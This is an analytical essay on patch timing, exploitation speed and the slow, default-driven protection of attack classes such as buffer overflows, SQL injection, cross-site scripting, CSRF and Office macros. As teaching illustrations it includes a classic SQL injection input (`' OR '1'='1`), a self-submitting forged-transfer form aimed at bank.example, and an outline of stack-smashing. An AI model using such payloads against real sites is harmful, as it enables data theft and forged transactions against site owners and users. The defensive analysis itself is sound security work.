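Patching speed matters only relative to how quickly attackers exploit flaws, and published figures for that differ sharply. The most quoted figure comes from Mandiant, Google's incident-response business. Qualys reports that Mandiant put the mean *time to exploit*, the time from a patch's release to the first known attack, at minus 1 day in 2024 and minus 7 days in 2025, meaning that on average the attack came before the patch.

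CISA's list and a similar one from the security firm VulnCheck show no such acceleration. Lbath and colleagues examined a decade of public records and conclude that the time from disclosure to attack "has not shifted noticeably so far".

The mean time from patch to first attack can be negative even when most attacks come after the patch. Suppose attackers first use nine flaws 5 days after the patch and a tenth 115 days before it. The mean is minus 7 days, while the median is plus 5. Some real cases are similarly extreme. Attackers used a flaw in the Windows kernel 182 days before its disclosure and one in WinRAR, a file-compression program, 110 days before. A few more such cases in a year would lower the mean even if attackers reacted no faster to newly published flaws.

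The sources also date attacks differently. Mandiant's investigators try to find out when an attack first happened, whereas many catalogue dates show only when the flaw was listed. Attackers used the Cisco flaw 30 days before its disclosure, but if a catalogue lists such a flaw on the day of disclosure, its time to exploit appears to be zero. Catalogue dates can therefore hide a trend towards attacks starting longer before disclosure, and we can't conclude from Mandiant's mean that attackers have become quicker at turning published flaws into attacks.

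Rapid7 found that KEV listings came sooner in 2025, which is some evidence that flaws are being exploited faster, or at least that exploitation is being detected faster. But the comparison covers only two years and a limited number of flaws. The rise in the number of exploited flaws is clearer. Rapid7 counted 146 newly disclosed serious flaws with confirmed exploitation in 2025, up from 71 in 2024.

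Qualys examined 52 KEV flaws for which it had a confirmed date of first exploitation. For 88% of them, the average organisation took longer to patch the flaw than attackers took to exploit it. Attackers had exploited 26 of the 52 before public disclosure and another three on the day of disclosure. Qualys acknowledges that these flaws may be unusually prominent, since they are the ones with complete histories.

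The comparison is also harsh on defenders because it sets the first attack against the average defender. A first attack before disclosure is often a quiet operation against a few targets, and most organisations are in danger only once many attackers have the method. GreyNoise, citing Verizon's 2025 report, puts the median time from disclosure to mass exploitation at five days for all KEV flaws and zero days for those in edge devices. At the 2025 pace, about seven in ten instances are still open on day 5, so defenders are too slow even by this fairer comparison, though by less.

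Patching late is still worth doing because unpatched machines remain targets for years. According to Zafran, Verizon found that about half of KEV flaws were under attack nearly all the time, and four in five of those were registered before 2024.

Attackers had been exploiting a WinRAR flaw for 110 days before its disclosure, and organisations then took an average of 137 days to patch it. Qualys adds the two periods and calls the 247 days the "average window of exposure". Faster patching could have shortened only the 137 days. A year after disclosure, about 15% of the affected systems were still vulnerable.

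### Did more disclosure bring more attacks?

Each published flaw also gives attackers information they can use against users who are slow to install the fix. The surge of AI-found flaws in 2026 could therefore have done harm even if vendors fixed every one before publishing it. Mosk (2026) tested this in *Does Frontier AI Strengthen Cyber Defense?* using Project Glasswing, the programme through which Anthropic gave selected organisations early access to Claude Mythos Preview.

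Mosk compared 13 large American participants, including Apple, Google and Microsoft, with Chinese technology firms such as Huawei and Lenovo, which Anthropic's terms exclude. Both groups' monthly disclosures stayed close to their 2025 averages until early 2026. The participants' disclosures nearly doubled in March, when they were already using the model, and exceeded four times the 2025 average by June. The Chinese firms had no comparable rise. Over the whole period, participants more than doubled their disclosures relative to the Chinese firms and took no longer to fix reported flaws.

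Mosk found no evidence that attackers took advantage. Before the launch, attackers exploited 1.4% of the participants' flaws within a month of disclosure. After the launch, that share fell by 0.9 percentage points, or about two thirds, relative to the Chinese firms. In a separate comparison with large firms outside China, the *number* of exploited flaws did not change.

The unchanged number of exploited flaws is better evidence than the falling share. If firms disclose 1,000 flaws and attackers exploit 14 of them, the share exploited is 1.4%. If AI then helps firms disclose another 1,500 that attackers never touch, the share drops to 0.56%, although attackers are doing as much damage as before. Most of the fall in Mosk's study could have happened this way. The unchanged number does suggest that the extra disclosures did not give attackers many new ways to attack.

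Mosk's more optimistic reading is that defenders found flaws before attackers did. The decline supports this reading because it was concentrated in *zero-days*, flaws that attackers were already using when the flaws became public. The probability that a disclosed flaw was a zero-day fell by about 70% relative to the Chinese firms and by about 60% relative to the large firms elsewhere. But adding many unexploited flaws to the total lowers this probability too. A fall in the number of zero-day attacks would be better evidence that defenders are getting ahead.

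The comparison group is another weakness. Anthropic chose the participants, and Chinese firms publish flaws under different rules. If China had restricted disclosure around the time of the launch, the participants' rise would look too large. Mosk checked for this and found that Chinese firms had begun publishing more of their own flaws, and that the share published by independent organisations had stayed the same. The comparison with firms outside China avoids the difference in rules but stops in May 2026, because Anthropic then extended access to about 150 more organisations. Outside researchers also moved from the participants' code to other companies' code, where they reported more flaws, so the programme somewhat affected the comparison firms too.

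The result may not apply to other software. Large firms such as Apple and Google can deliver many fixes through automatic updates, while a small open-source project must wait for others to notice a release. Mosk's main measure also covers only the first month, and 35% of KEV instances were still open at day 28 in 2025. An attacker who returns to one of the new flaws a year later would not appear in the results. Mosk observed when vendors released fixes, not when users installed them, so the study doesn't show whether users were quick enough or attackers had better targets.

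A flaw enters the KEV list only if somebody exploits it. If disclosures double but the number of exploited flaws stays the same, administrators have more routine patching to do but no more urgent patching.

### PHP2Shell against the clock

The PHP flaws of October 2026 are a useful test of these figures because most of the dates are known. In the table, day 0 is the day the fix was released. The federal tiers and the shares still open are benchmarks, and they assume that the deadline and the KEV clock both start on day 0.

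| Date in 2026 | Day | Event or benchmark |
|---|---|---|
| 11 August | −71 | A researcher privately reports a working attack |
| 17 October | −4 | First recorded attack attempts |
| 21 October | 0 | PHP's maintainers release the fixes |
| 24 October | 3 | End of the shortest federal tier |
| 28 October | 7 | 68% of instances still open at the 2025 KEV pace |
| 4 November | 14 | End of the middle federal tier |
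| 18 November | 28 | 35% still open at the 2025 KEV pace |
| 20 December | 60 | End of the longest federal tier |

The time to exploit was minus 4 days by Mandiant's measure. It would be zero or more if a catalogue listed the flaw on or after 21 October and used the listing date as the date of the attack. Neither figure measures how many servers attackers took over, because an attempt can fail and the first attempts may have reached very few servers.

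An agency that met a three-day deadline would still have been exposed for a week after the first recorded attempts, and even an owner who installed the fix within minutes of its release would have been exposed for four days. Before a fix exists, owners can only reduce the risk by other means, such as filtering suspicious requests or taking a server offline.

PHP servers may not follow the KEV curve closely. A hosting company can update thousands of websites at once, which would make patching faster than on company laptops. But many small sites have no administrator watching for security news, and servers running PHP 8.1 or older must move to a newer version, which can break the programs on them. Censys' scans can measure patching directly, but the servers that reveal their PHP version may not be typical. Some Linux distributors also add security fixes to old versions without changing the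 version number, so a patched server can look vulnerable in a scan.

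## Memory corruption: decades of partial protection

Installing the October PHP release fixes two flaws on one server but doesn't protect against the next flaw of the same kind. Protecting against a whole class of attacks takes far longer. One of the classes with the longest records is *memory corruption*, in which an attacker's input makes a program overwrite memory it shouldn't. The programming mistakes that allow this are called *memory-safety flaws*.

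### How a buffer overflow works

The best-known form of memory corruption is the buffer overflow. A *buffer* is a stretch of memory that a program sets aside for data, such as a user's name. The programming language C lets a program copy data into a buffer without checking that it fits.

Suppose part of a program sets aside 64 bytes for a name. Nearby, the computer keeps a *return address*, the location of the instruction to run when this part has finished. Both are in an area of memory called the *stack*. In simplified form:

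| Bytes | Purpose | After normal input | After the attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1–64 | Buffer for the name | "Ada", then unused space | The attacker's instructions |
| 65–72 | Return address | A location in the main program | The location of byte 1 |

The attacker sends 72 bytes instead of a name. The first 64 fill the buffer and the last 8 replace the return address. When this part of the program finishes, the processor reads the return address, jumps to byte 1 and runs the attacker's instructions with all the program's privileges.

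The attack works only if the program lacks a length check, the attacker knows where byte 1 is, and the processor runs data as if it were code. Most protections have targeted the last two conditions without adding the missing check.

### From 1972 to 1996

A 1972 planning study on computer security described an operating system that copied data without properly checking the addresses, which let a user insert code and take over the machine. *Buffer Overflows and History* (Shostack + Friends Blog, 2008) cites the passage as proof that people understood buffer overflows by 1972. One could argue for a later date, since the missing check was on addresses, not length.

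The Morris worm, a program that copied itself from computer to computer, brought memory corruption to public attention on 2 November 1988. *The Internet Worm* (Spafford, 1989) describes how it attacked one of its targets, fingerd, a program that answered questions about a computer's users. Fingerd read each request with gets, a standard C routine that does not check the length of its input. The worm sent 536 bytes, which overran the buffer and changed the return address to point back into it. The instructions there gave the worm a command line on the machine. The attack worked only on VAX computers, and on Sun machines it crashed fingerd.

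By about 9 p.m. the next day, some 28 hours after the worm appeared, programmers at Berkeley had released patches for all the flaws it used. Spafford still expected more flaws of this kind. Experienced programmers knew that gets and similar routines were dangerous but kept using them, and the forthcoming official standard for C included them.

Attacks became common only after someone published clear instructions. Aleph One explained the technique in *Smashing The Stack For Fun And Profit*, published in the 8 November 1996 issue of the hacker magazine Phrack. Cowan, who invented one of the main defences, calls the article a "cook book" in his retrospective talk *StackGuard* and says attacks were rampant afterwards. Buffer overflows accounted for 9 of CERT's 13 security advisories in 1998, according to *Buffer Overflows*, by Cowan, Wagle and colleagues.

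### Protections and ways around them

In 1997, a programmer known as Solar Designer released a Linux patch that stopped the processor from running code stored on the stack. In the example above, the jump to byte 1 would fail. Attackers responded by putting their instructions in the *heap*, a separate area for longer-lived data. They could also point the return address at code already in memory, such as the part of the standard C library that starts other programs.

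The protection was difficult to extend to the rest of memory because the x86 processors in most personal computers could not mark individual pages as non-executable. Extending the protection also broke some applications (Bellovin, 2007).

Cowan's group announced StackGuard on the Bugtraq mailing list in December 1997. StackGuard modifies the compiler, the tool that turns source code into a program the computer can run. The resulting program keeps a check value, or *canary*, between the buffer and the return address. An overflow that reaches the return address also changes the canary. The program checks the canary before it jumps to that address and shuts down if the value is wrong. An intern wrote the prototype in a few days, using fewer than 100 lines of code.

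In 1999, an attacker called Emsi bypassed the canary by changing a different saved value in front of it, which sent the program to a fake return address. Cowan's group blocked this attack by tying the canary to the correct return address. Canaries still did not stop heap overflows, so attackers turned to those.

*Address randomisation*, which the Linux project PaX introduced in 2001, loads parts of a program at different locations each time it runs, so an attacker no longer knows which address to jump to. Attackers responded by filling the heap with copies of their instructions, each preceded by a long run of instructions that do nothing, so that a jump to almost anywhere in the heap would lead to one of the copies.

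Randomisation hides the code already in memory, and non-executable memory stops attackers from running code they add, so each protects against attacks the other misses. But web browsers and some other programs generate code as they run, so they need memory that is both writable and executable. Attackers learned to get their instructions into that memory, which defeated both protections.

Jones and Kelly built a complete defence, a C compiler that checked every buffer access, but Cowan says it made programs 3 to 30 times slower. *Memory-safe languages* such as Java and Rust have these checks built in, so ordinary code can't write past the end of a buffer.

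| Protection | First published | First mainstream adoption | Lag |
|---|---|---|---|
| Stack canaries | 1997 | 2003, Microsoft's compiler | 6 years |
| Non-executable memory | 1997 | 2004, Windows XP Service Pack 2 | 7 years |
| Address randomisation | 2001 | 2007, Windows Vista | 6 years |
| Memory-safe languages | 1995 at the latest, with Java | Still not the default for low-level code in most systems | More than 30 years |

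The dates for non-executable memory and randomisation come from later accounts, not from documents of the time, and they are disputed. Cowan, for example, says Windows XP Service Pack 2 also included randomisation, which would cut the lag for randomisation to three years. First adoption was also limited. By default, Windows XP applied non-executable memory mainly to its own components, and mainstream Linux systems got canaries several years after Windows did.

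Measuring the lag for safe languages from Java's release is harsh, because Java was never a practical replacement for C in the lowest layers of an operating system. Rust is a practical replacement, and its first stable version came out in 2015. Counting from then, the lag is 11 years so far.

### Android's new code

Android shows that memory-safe languages can reduce memory-safety flaws in a large system. These flaws made up 76% of Android's vulnerabilities in 2019 and 24% in 2024, according to Google (2024). *Rust in Android* (Vander Stoep, 2025) reported that the share had fallen below 20% for the first time.

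Some of the drop in share came from an increase in other kinds of flaw. The Hacker News (2025) reports 223 memory-safety flaws in 2019, and Google projected 36 for all of 2024. Together with the percentages, these counts imply that the number of other flaws rose from about 70 to about 114. If that number had stayed at 70, the 2024 share would have been 34% instead of 24%. Even so, the number of memory-safety flaws fell by 84%.

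Google achieved this without rewriting Android. Around 2019, the team began to favour safe languages for new code and left most old code alone except for bug fixes. Most of Android's code was still unsafe in 2024. *Memory Safe Languages in Android 13* (2022) reports that Rust made up 21% of new low-level code. By 2025, Android developers at Google were adding slightly more Rust than C++, an unsafe language descended from C.

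Replacing only new code works because most flaws are in new or recently changed code. As code ages, people find and fix its flaws. If flaws last an average of L years, the share still present after t years is e^(−t/L). Google estimates that five-year-old code has 3.4 to 7.4 times fewer flaws per line than new code, which corresponds to average lifetimes of about 4.1 and 2.5 years. At those rates, 1,000 flaws in code that nobody adds to would fall to between 140 and 290 after five years, and to between 20 and 90 after ten.

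In Google's simulation of a similar project, the number of memory-safety flaws fell even as the amount of unsafe code grew, because developers added unsafe code more slowly and flaws in older code disappeared faster than new ones were introduced. Google was also making its existing C and C++ code safer during these years, so the switch of languages may not fully explain Android's results.

Rust has held up well in Android. Vander Stoep counts one potential memory-safety flaw in about 5 million lines of Android's Rust, or 0.2 per million lines, against roughly 1,000 per million in its C and C++ code. A rate based on a single flaw is very uncertain, but even the top of a 95% confidence interval would be about 1.1 per million. A bigger problem with the comparison is that researchers have had much longer to find flaws in the C and C++ code.

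The one flaw was a buffer overflow in an image library, and Google fixed it before release. It was in a section of code marked "unsafe", where Rust lets programmers bypass some of its checks. About 4% of Android's Rust code is in such sections. An attacker could not have exploited the flaw on phones that use Android's standard memory allocator, because the allocator surrounds large buffers with off-limits memory and the overflow would have crashed the program. The older protections are therefore still useful as a second layer.

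Rust also saved Google's developers work. They rolled back medium and large Rust changes about a quarter as often as similar C++ changes, and Rust changes spent 25% less time in review. Earlier protections tended to reduce speed or compatibility, which gave vendors a reason to delay adopting them.

### Old flaws in old code

A weakness in Google's argument about ageing code is that researchers can calculate a flaw's lifetime only if somebody has found it. Leaving out undiscovered flaws, which are censored cases, makes the estimated average lifetime too short.

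The rise in disclosures in 2026 suggests that many such flaws remained. Lbath and colleagues found that people reported severe flaws at least ten years old at 6 to 11 times the previous year's monthly rate between July and October 2026. The affected software included the Linux kernel, Windows and open-source packages. AI agents also found flaws in code that experts and automated tools had examined for years.

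These figures don't show that old code is as risky as new code. Most of the increase followed the overall rise in reports, and the share of old flaws among those with a known age rose by only 6 to 9 percentage points. The count also covers severe flaws of every kind, not just memory corruption. Researchers can work out a flaw's age from most Linux kernel records, but from only 2 to 3% of other records.

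But the figures suggest that some old code looked safe partly because its remaining flaws were hard to find. With better search tools, those flaws could now be removed faster than Google assumes in its model, if maintainers fix what the tools find. Lbath and colleagues have so far seen no sign that the flaws are running out.

Android's share for 2025 predates most of this surge. Google's November 2026 update fixed more than 200 flaws (Arghire, *Android's November 2026 Updates Patch Over 200 Vulnerabilities*, 2026), compared with the roughly 150 implied by Google's figures for all of 2024, though the two counts may not cover the same components. The December update fixed 85 more. According to RodHat's *Android 17 QPR2* (2026), one of these was a video decoder flaw that could cause writes outside the decoder's memory and let an attacker run code without any action by the user.

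### How long was the class lag?

Class lag ends when a protection is on by default in most deployed systems. For buffer overflows, that was probably around 2008. In October of that year, Shostack + Friends Blog described the defences built into compilers and operating systems as "now widespread". One blog's remark is weak evidence for the date, but it fits the adoption dates above.

Under a stricter definition, the lag would end only when the attack class had nearly disappeared. That hasn't happened for memory corruption, so its lag is still censored.

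| Clock starts | Until default protection was widespread, about 2008 | Until near-disappearance |
|---|---|---|
| Early description, 1972 | 36 years | More than 54 years |
| Morris worm, 1988 | 20 years | More than 38 years |
| Aleph One's article, 1996 | 12 years | More than 30 years |

The stricter definition adds at least 18 years to each estimate, and the choice of starting date changes the result by up to 24 years. Someone who predicted in 1996 that the industry would deal with buffer overflows by 2010 would have been right by the looser definition but badly wrong by the stricter one.

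## SQL injection, cross-site scripting and cross-site request forgery

SQL injection, cross-site scripting and cross-site request forgery are attacks on websites that became public between 1998 and 2001, but the lag before fixes were deployed has differed among them. In 2020, browser makers turned on a protection against cross-site request forgery for about half of all web users. Protection against the other two still depends largely on what each developer does.

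### How the three attacks work

SQL injection takes its name from SQL, the language in which many websites query their databases. Suppose a school's website looks up students with this line, in which `+` joins pieces of text:

`"SELECT * FROM students WHERE lastname = '" + name + "'"`

If a visitor enters `' OR '1'='1` as the name, the condition becomes `lastname = '' OR '1'='1'`, which is always true, so the database returns every student. eWeek's *Inoculating Yourself Against SQL Injection* prints a similar line, and its author admits having written such code.

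The fix is a *parameterised query*, such as `SELECT * FROM students WHERE lastname = ?`. The program sends the name separately, and the database never treats it as part of the command. (Language models have no such separation, which makes prompt injection harder to fix.)

*Cross-site scripting* injects code into a web page instead of a database query. A search page might contain this line:

`"<p>Results for " + search + "</p>"`

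An attacker sends someone a link in which the search text is a `<script>` tag with code inside. The victim's browser runs the code as if the site had written it, so the code can act in the victim's account. The basic fix is *output escaping*, which replaces `<` with `&lt;` so that the browser displays the character instead of reading it as the start of a tag. Content Security Policy (CSP), a browser feature that restricts which scripts may run on a page, can block an injected script even where a developer forgot to escape the text.

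*Cross-site request forgery* relies on cookies, the small pieces of data that keep a user logged in. Browsers traditionally attached a site's cookies to every request to that site, including requests started by another site's page. An attacker's page could therefore contain a hidden form that submits itself:

`<form method="POST" action="https://bank.example/transfer">`

If the victim is logged in, the bank receives what looks like a genuine order. To prevent this, the bank can put an unpredictable value, or *token*, in its own forms and reject any request without it. It can instead mark its cookies with the *SameSite* attribute, so that the browser withholds them from requests that start on other sites.

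### A complete fix, one query at a time

rain.forest.puppy (1998), in *NT Web Technology Vulnerabilities*, described SQL injection in Phrack on 25 December 1998. The author's real name is Jeff Forristal, and eSecurity Planet's *How Was SQL Injection Discovered?* (2013) credits him with the first public discussion of the attack. In February 2000, he explained on Bugtraq how he had used it to break into the security website PacketStorm. That post, *How I hacked PacketStorm*, included a section on the solution.

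The fix for SQL injection, parameterised queries, was older than the published attack. Java's standard database library had offered them since 1997. They also prevent nearly all SQL injection where they are used. The main exception is table and column names, which a placeholder cannot stand for, so a site that lets users choose a column to sort by needs a separate check.

But nobody could install this fix for everyone, because developers had to find and rewrite every query that joined user input to SQL text. Missing one could expose the whole database. If a developer gets each query right 99% of the time, a program with 200 queries has a 13% chance (0.99^200) of having no mistakes.

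Attackers could also search for the mistakes automatically. Automated SQL injection reportedly compromised more than half a million websites in one year, according to the Pwnie Awards, which honour and mock events in computer security.

SQL injection attacks continue in 2026. In May, CISA added an SQL injection flaw in Drupal, a widely used system for managing websites, to its KEV list (The Hacker News). TechRadar's *This 'classic' decades-old SQL injection flaw could let hackers take over* reported in August that intruders had used SQL injection against an Oracle database to run commands on a Windows server. In November, the makers of WHMCS, billing software for web-hosting companies, fixed a flaw that could expose customer records and administrators' password hashes to an attacker without a login (The Hacker News, *WHMCS SQL Injection Could Expose Customer Data and Admin Password Hashes*).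 AI agents sent to collect public data also appear to have tried SQL injection on American and Canadian government websites (Kovacs 2026, *AI Agents Aimed SQL Injection at US and Canadian Government Sites*).

The two best-known rankings of software weaknesses give conflicting evidence on whether SQL injection is declining. OWASP, a non-profit that publishes guidance on web security, ranked injection fifth in its 2025 list, according to heise's *Awareness for Web Security*. The injection category has also included cross-site scripting since 2021. MITRE, the non-profit that maintains the Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE), ranks SQL injection, cross-site scripting and cross-site request forgery higher than it did in 2019.

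| Attack class | CWE rank, 2019 | CWE rank, 2025 | KEV flaws in the 2025 data |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cross-site scripting | 2 | 1 | 7 |
| SQL injection | 6 | 2 | 4 |
| Cross-site request forgery | 9 | 3 | 0 |

The 2019 ranks come from Security Magazine and the rest from MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025). MITRE ranks weaknesses by the number and severity of reported flaws, so a class can rise in the list while becoming rarer in new websites. MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Key Insights* (2025) reports that SQL injection records increased by almost 1,000 in a year and cross-site scripting records by more than 3,000. However, the total number of CVE records was also growing, and MITRE had changed its method. When MITRE (2025) ranked weaknesses by known exploitation, cross-site scripting came tenth, and SQL injection and cross-site request forgery were outside the top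 ten.

New websites probably contain fewer of these flaws. Most developers now build on *frameworks*, collections of ready-made code that handle database queries and page output. The security firm NVISO says in *OWASP Top 10 2025* (2026) that introducing SQL injection or cross-site scripting in such applications "almost requires additional effort".

CISA is less forgiving. *CISA review makes the case for eliminating vulnerability classes* (Zorz, 2026) reports that 41.5% of KEV entries involve "stubborn" weaknesses, types that have been in MITRE's top 25 nearly every year since 2019. CISA blames organisational culture, since the technical solutions are known. That criticism is fair when vendors still ship such flaws in new products, but even with a better culture, they would still have to rewrite the queries in old ones.

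### Policies that allow the attack

CERT published a warning about cross-site scripting in February 2000. Escaping protects against it but has the same drawback as parameterised queries, since developers must apply it everywhere a page displays untrusted text. Content Security Policy (CSP), which researchers proposed in 2010, was meant to limit the damage from any place they missed.

A Content Security Policy (CSP) blocks most injected scripts only if it forbids *inline* scripts, meaning code written directly into the page. Many sites rely on inline scripts, so CSP has a setting called `unsafe-inline` that permits them, including any that an attacker injects.

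In *Complex Security Policy*, Roth, Barron and colleagues used the Internet Archive to reconstruct the Content Security Policies of 10,000 popular sites from 2012 to 2018. At the end of that period, 1,032 sites enforced a policy, but only 421 of those policies tried to restrict scripts, and 378 of the 421 allowed unsafe inline code. That left 43 sites, or 4% of those with a policy, and some of these had other serious gaps. The policies on the other sites could still be useful for other purposes, such as making browsers use encrypted connections.

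Airbnb's experience shows why a working policy was so rare. The company began testing one in November 2014 with a list of 17 approved sources for scripts. By March 2015 the list had grown to 21, and Airbnb then replaced it with a rule approving every source that used an encrypted connection. It started enforcing a policy in May 2015, switched it off eight days later and restored it after another two weeks. Over the next two and a half years the company changed the policy 222 times, mostly to keep up with its own inline scripts, while still accepting code from any encrypted source. It introduced a limited list in January 2018 but withdrew it after three days. In March 2018 it introduced one that lasted, more than three years after its first test.

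A carefully kept list of approved sources can still fail if one of them changes hands. Roth and colleagues found that 50 of 373 sites with such lists had approved at least one domain that an attacker might be able to abuse. Some of these domains had expired, so anyone could have bought them, and others were misspelled.

Report URI's *10 years of watching the web* has newer figures, from a crawl of the top million websites on 13 June 2026. Of the 819,002 sites that responded, 170,057 had a policy, up from about 1,400 in 2016. But 46.8% of the policies contained `unsafe-inline`.

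| | Roth and colleagues, 2018 | Report URI, June 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Sites studied | 10,000 | 819,002 |
| Sites with a policy | 1,032 (10%) | 170,057 (21%) |
| Policies allowing unsafe inline code | 378 (37%) | 79,464 (47%) |
| Sites using nonces | 24 (0.2%) | 41,936 (5%) |

These studies show no sign that unsafe policies became less common. As a share of all policies, they made up 37% in 2018 and 47% in the later study. The 90% figure for 2018 is not comparable with the 47% because it covers only policies that restrict scripts.

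The 46.8% is also a poor estimate of how many policies fail to stop cross-site scripting. Modern browsers ignore `unsafe-inline` when a policy contains a *nonce*, a random value that a site puts in both its policy and its own script tags. If every policy with a nonce also contained `unsafe-inline` to support old browsers, the setting would take effect in only 22% of policies. But the 46.8% leaves out policies that don't restrict scripts at all, which also offer no protection against the attack. These made up 59% of policies in 2018.

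The growth in nonces is more encouraging. Nonces let a site approve its own inline scripts without approving all inline scripts. The share of sites using them has risen about twentyfold, though the two samples differ, and is still only one in twenty.

Report URI, which sells tools for monitoring CSP, argues that site owners lack information about which scripts their pages run. It recommends testing in report-only mode, in which the browser reports violations without blocking anything. In Roth and colleagues' data, only 130 of the 449 sites (29%) that tested a content-restricting policy this way went on to enforce one, which suggests that information is often not enough. Many owners probably learned from the reports how much of their site they would have to rewrite.

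### A default in the browser

Cross-site request forgery has been publicly known since at least 2001, according to Compagna, Jonker and colleagues in *A preliminary study on the adoption and effectiveness of SameSite cookies*. At first, each site had to add its own anti-forgery tokens. Frameworks gradually began to supply them, and OWASP dropped the attack from its top ten in 2017, partly because more frameworks had secure default settings.

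In 2006, researchers proposed a tool that removed cookies from suspicious cross-site requests, but users would have had to install it. Google brought a similar idea to Chrome ten years later as the SameSite attribute. The main dates come from Khodayari and Pellegrino's *The State of the SameSite* and from Compagna and colleagues.

| Date | Change in Chrome |
|---|---|
| April 2016 | Sites can set SameSite, but nothing changes for sites that don't |
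| September 2019 | Chrome starts warning developers about cookies without the attribute |
| 17 February 2020 | Google begins applying SameSite by default, for a limited group of users |
| 3 April 2020 | Google halts the rollout and then withdraws the default because of the Covid-19 pandemic |
| 14 July 2020 | The rollout restarts |
| 11 August 2020 | The default reaches all the intended users |

Few sites used the SameSite attribute while it was optional. In the spring of 2020, four years after its introduction, 92.3% of the 6,180 sites that Compagna and colleagues examined did not set it on their login cookies. Many site owners may have thought tokens were enough, but the default protected their sites with or without them.

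To estimate the effect of the SameSite default, Compagna and colleagues classified 991 requests that changed something on a server, such as an account setting. SameSite could protect 86% of them. Because 1.9% of sites had switched the protection off, the researchers estimated that the default would cover about 84%. Browsers without the default would cover only about 5%, because few sites had set the attribute themselves. These figures describe potential coverage, not attacks prevented, and many of the requests probably also had tokens.

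Compagna and colleagues estimated that 51.6% of users had a browser that applied the default, so the average coverage across all users was just under half. Firefox had announced the same change but still sent cookies by default when Khodayari and Pellegrino studied it.

Google also left gaps in the default on purpose. Browsers normally use a GET request to open a page and a POST request to submit a change. The default still allows cookies when a link on another site opens a page with GET, since otherwise people following links would often appear to be logged out. But Khodayari and Pellegrino found that about 10% of state-changing requests on the top 1,000 sites used GET, and they could forge 7 of the 264 they tested. Some other sites, including PayPal and IMDb, accepted GET for a request meant to use POST, so an attacker could switch the method.

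Another gap arises because Chrome sends a new cookie with cross-site POST requests for the first two minutes after a site sets it. Chrome does this to avoid breaking services that let people log in with, say, a Google account. An attacker's page can trigger a fresh login, which creates a new cookie, and then forge a request within those two minutes. Khodayari and Pellegrino found that 49% of the top 10,000 sites used login providers that made this possible.

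Sites can also opt out. By March 2021, 18% of the top 1,000 sites had set at least some cookies to allow all cross-site requests, compared with 3.7% of the wider sample. Opting out can be legitimate, such as for a payment service that other sites embed. But when Compagna and colleagues tested 20 sites that had switched off the protection for all their login cookies, they found request forgery flaws on 9.

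The number of reported flaws has not fallen since the browser default arrived. MITRE's data for the 2025 list link 1,750 flaws to request forgery, up from 1,301 the year before. A researcher can still report a missing token even when most browsers would block the attack, so flaw counts are a bad measure of users' exposure to this class. None of the 1,750 was on the KEV list. The browser default may be part of the reason. Another reason is that request forgery needs a logged-in victim to visit the attacker's page, which makes it less useful to criminals than an attack they can launch directly at thousands of servers.

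### Do defaults explain the difference?

The class lags depend on what counts as protection, but request forgery has the shortest on any reasonable reading.

| Attack class | First public description | Protection on by default in most systems | Class lag |
|---|---|---|---|
| SQL injection | 1998 | Not shown; common in new frameworks | More than 27 years |
| Cross-site scripting | 2000 | Not shown; common in new frameworks | More than 26 years |
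| Cross-site request forgery | 2001 | About 2020, through browsers | About 19 years |

The first two lags could be shorter than the table implies, because frameworks may have brought parameterised queries and automatic escaping to a majority of sites some years ago. No survey measures how many deployed sites use either. The SQL injection lag could start earlier than 1998, since heise calls the flaw older than the web.

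Report URI sees the same pattern across web security. It argues that protections infrastructure companies can turn on for their customers have spread, while those that need continuing attention from each site have stalled. Its main example of success is HTTPS, the encrypted form of web traffic, which grew from 62,043 sites in 2015 to 658,038 in 2026, or 80.3% of those that responded. Its example of a stalled protection is DMARC, an email standard that lets a domain's owner tell other mail systems to reject messages that fake the domain's address. Of the 398,597 sites that publish a DMARC record, 51.4% monitor fakes without asking anyone to block them, so only about 24% of all responding sites enforce the standard.

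The comparison supports the claim less well than it first appears. HTTPS spread through a decade of work by browser makers, hosting companies and providers of free, automated certificates, not through a single change. Some sites in monitoring mode may be preparing to enforce DMARC, and a single crawl can't distinguish them from sites that have given up. Opt-in settings also sometimes spread. About 31% of sites now send HSTS, an instruction telling browsers to use only HTTPS, although just a fifth of those meet all the conditions for the strongest version.

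A more serious objection is that the problems that got defaults were the easy ones. A hosting company can encrypt a customer's traffic without knowing much about the site. Before enforcing DMARC, a company must identify every service that sends email in its name, or its invoices and newsletters may not arrive. CSP also requires knowledge of the site, because a browser can't determine which scripts the site needs. Comparing HTTPS with DMARC or CSP therefore mixes the effect of a default with the difficulty of the task.

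SameSite offers a better test, because the protection was the same before and after browsers made it the default. When each site had to turn it on, fewer than 8% set any value on their login cookies. After the change, Khodayari and Pellegrino found that 80.7% of sites relied on the browser's default, a difference that the difficulty of the problem can't explain.

Easy protections can also go largely unused when they aren't on by default. Site owners can add the prefix `__Host-` or `__Secure-` to a cookie's name so that browsers reject the cookie unless it meets certain security conditions. The prefixes are free and far simpler to adopt than CSP, yet fewer than 1% of the cookie-setting sites in Report URI's crawl used them.

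SameSite was not an especially easy default to introduce either. Khodayari and Pellegrino examined 633 cross-site requests that the change could affect and found that 19% no longer worked properly after the rollout. Most of these were for advertising, and only 1 of 81 login functions failed. Google could accept these failures after four years of preparation and with an exception for new cookies. A browser that suddenly blocked all inline scripts would break far more. Among the 378 sites with unsafe inline policies in 2018, at least 48% had inline code on their front page that could not be allowed using nonces.

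The objection is therefore right about which protections can become defaults, but a default still has an effect once it exists. SameSite worked because a browser can identify where a request started and apply one rule to every site. A database can't distinguish a visitor's input from the rest of a finished SQL query, so the program that builds the query has to provide the protection. Framework developers can make safe queries the default for new programs, but someone still has to rewrite the old ones.

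## Office macros and AI model files that run code

Office documents and AI model files can both carry commands that run when someone opens them, even though they look like data. Microsoft took about 28 years to block such commands by default in Office files from the internet. The comparable change for AI models took between 4 and 13 years, depending on the starting date, and many users still load models without that protection.

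### Macros that ran without asking

A *macro* is a small program stored in a document, for instance to format a report. In 1995, Word ran any macro named AutoOpen as soon as a user opened the document, without requiring the user's approval. A macro could also change how Word worked and copy itself into other documents, so it could spread as a virus.

The idea of a macro virus is older than Word's macros. According to Virus Bulletin (1995), people had described such viruses for the spreadsheet program Lotus 1-2-3 before the early 1990s. Muttik's *Throwback Thursday* (1999) credits Joel McNamara with the first real one, a demonstration from December 1994. Concept, the first to spread in public, appeared in the summer of 1995. It copied itself into documents when users chose "Save As" and did little else. Microsoft (1995) called it a "prank" and offered a tool to find it. By January 1998, there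 were more than 1,000 macro viruses and variants, according to *Macro Virus Update* (1998), a bulletin from CIAC, the US Department of Energy's incident response team.

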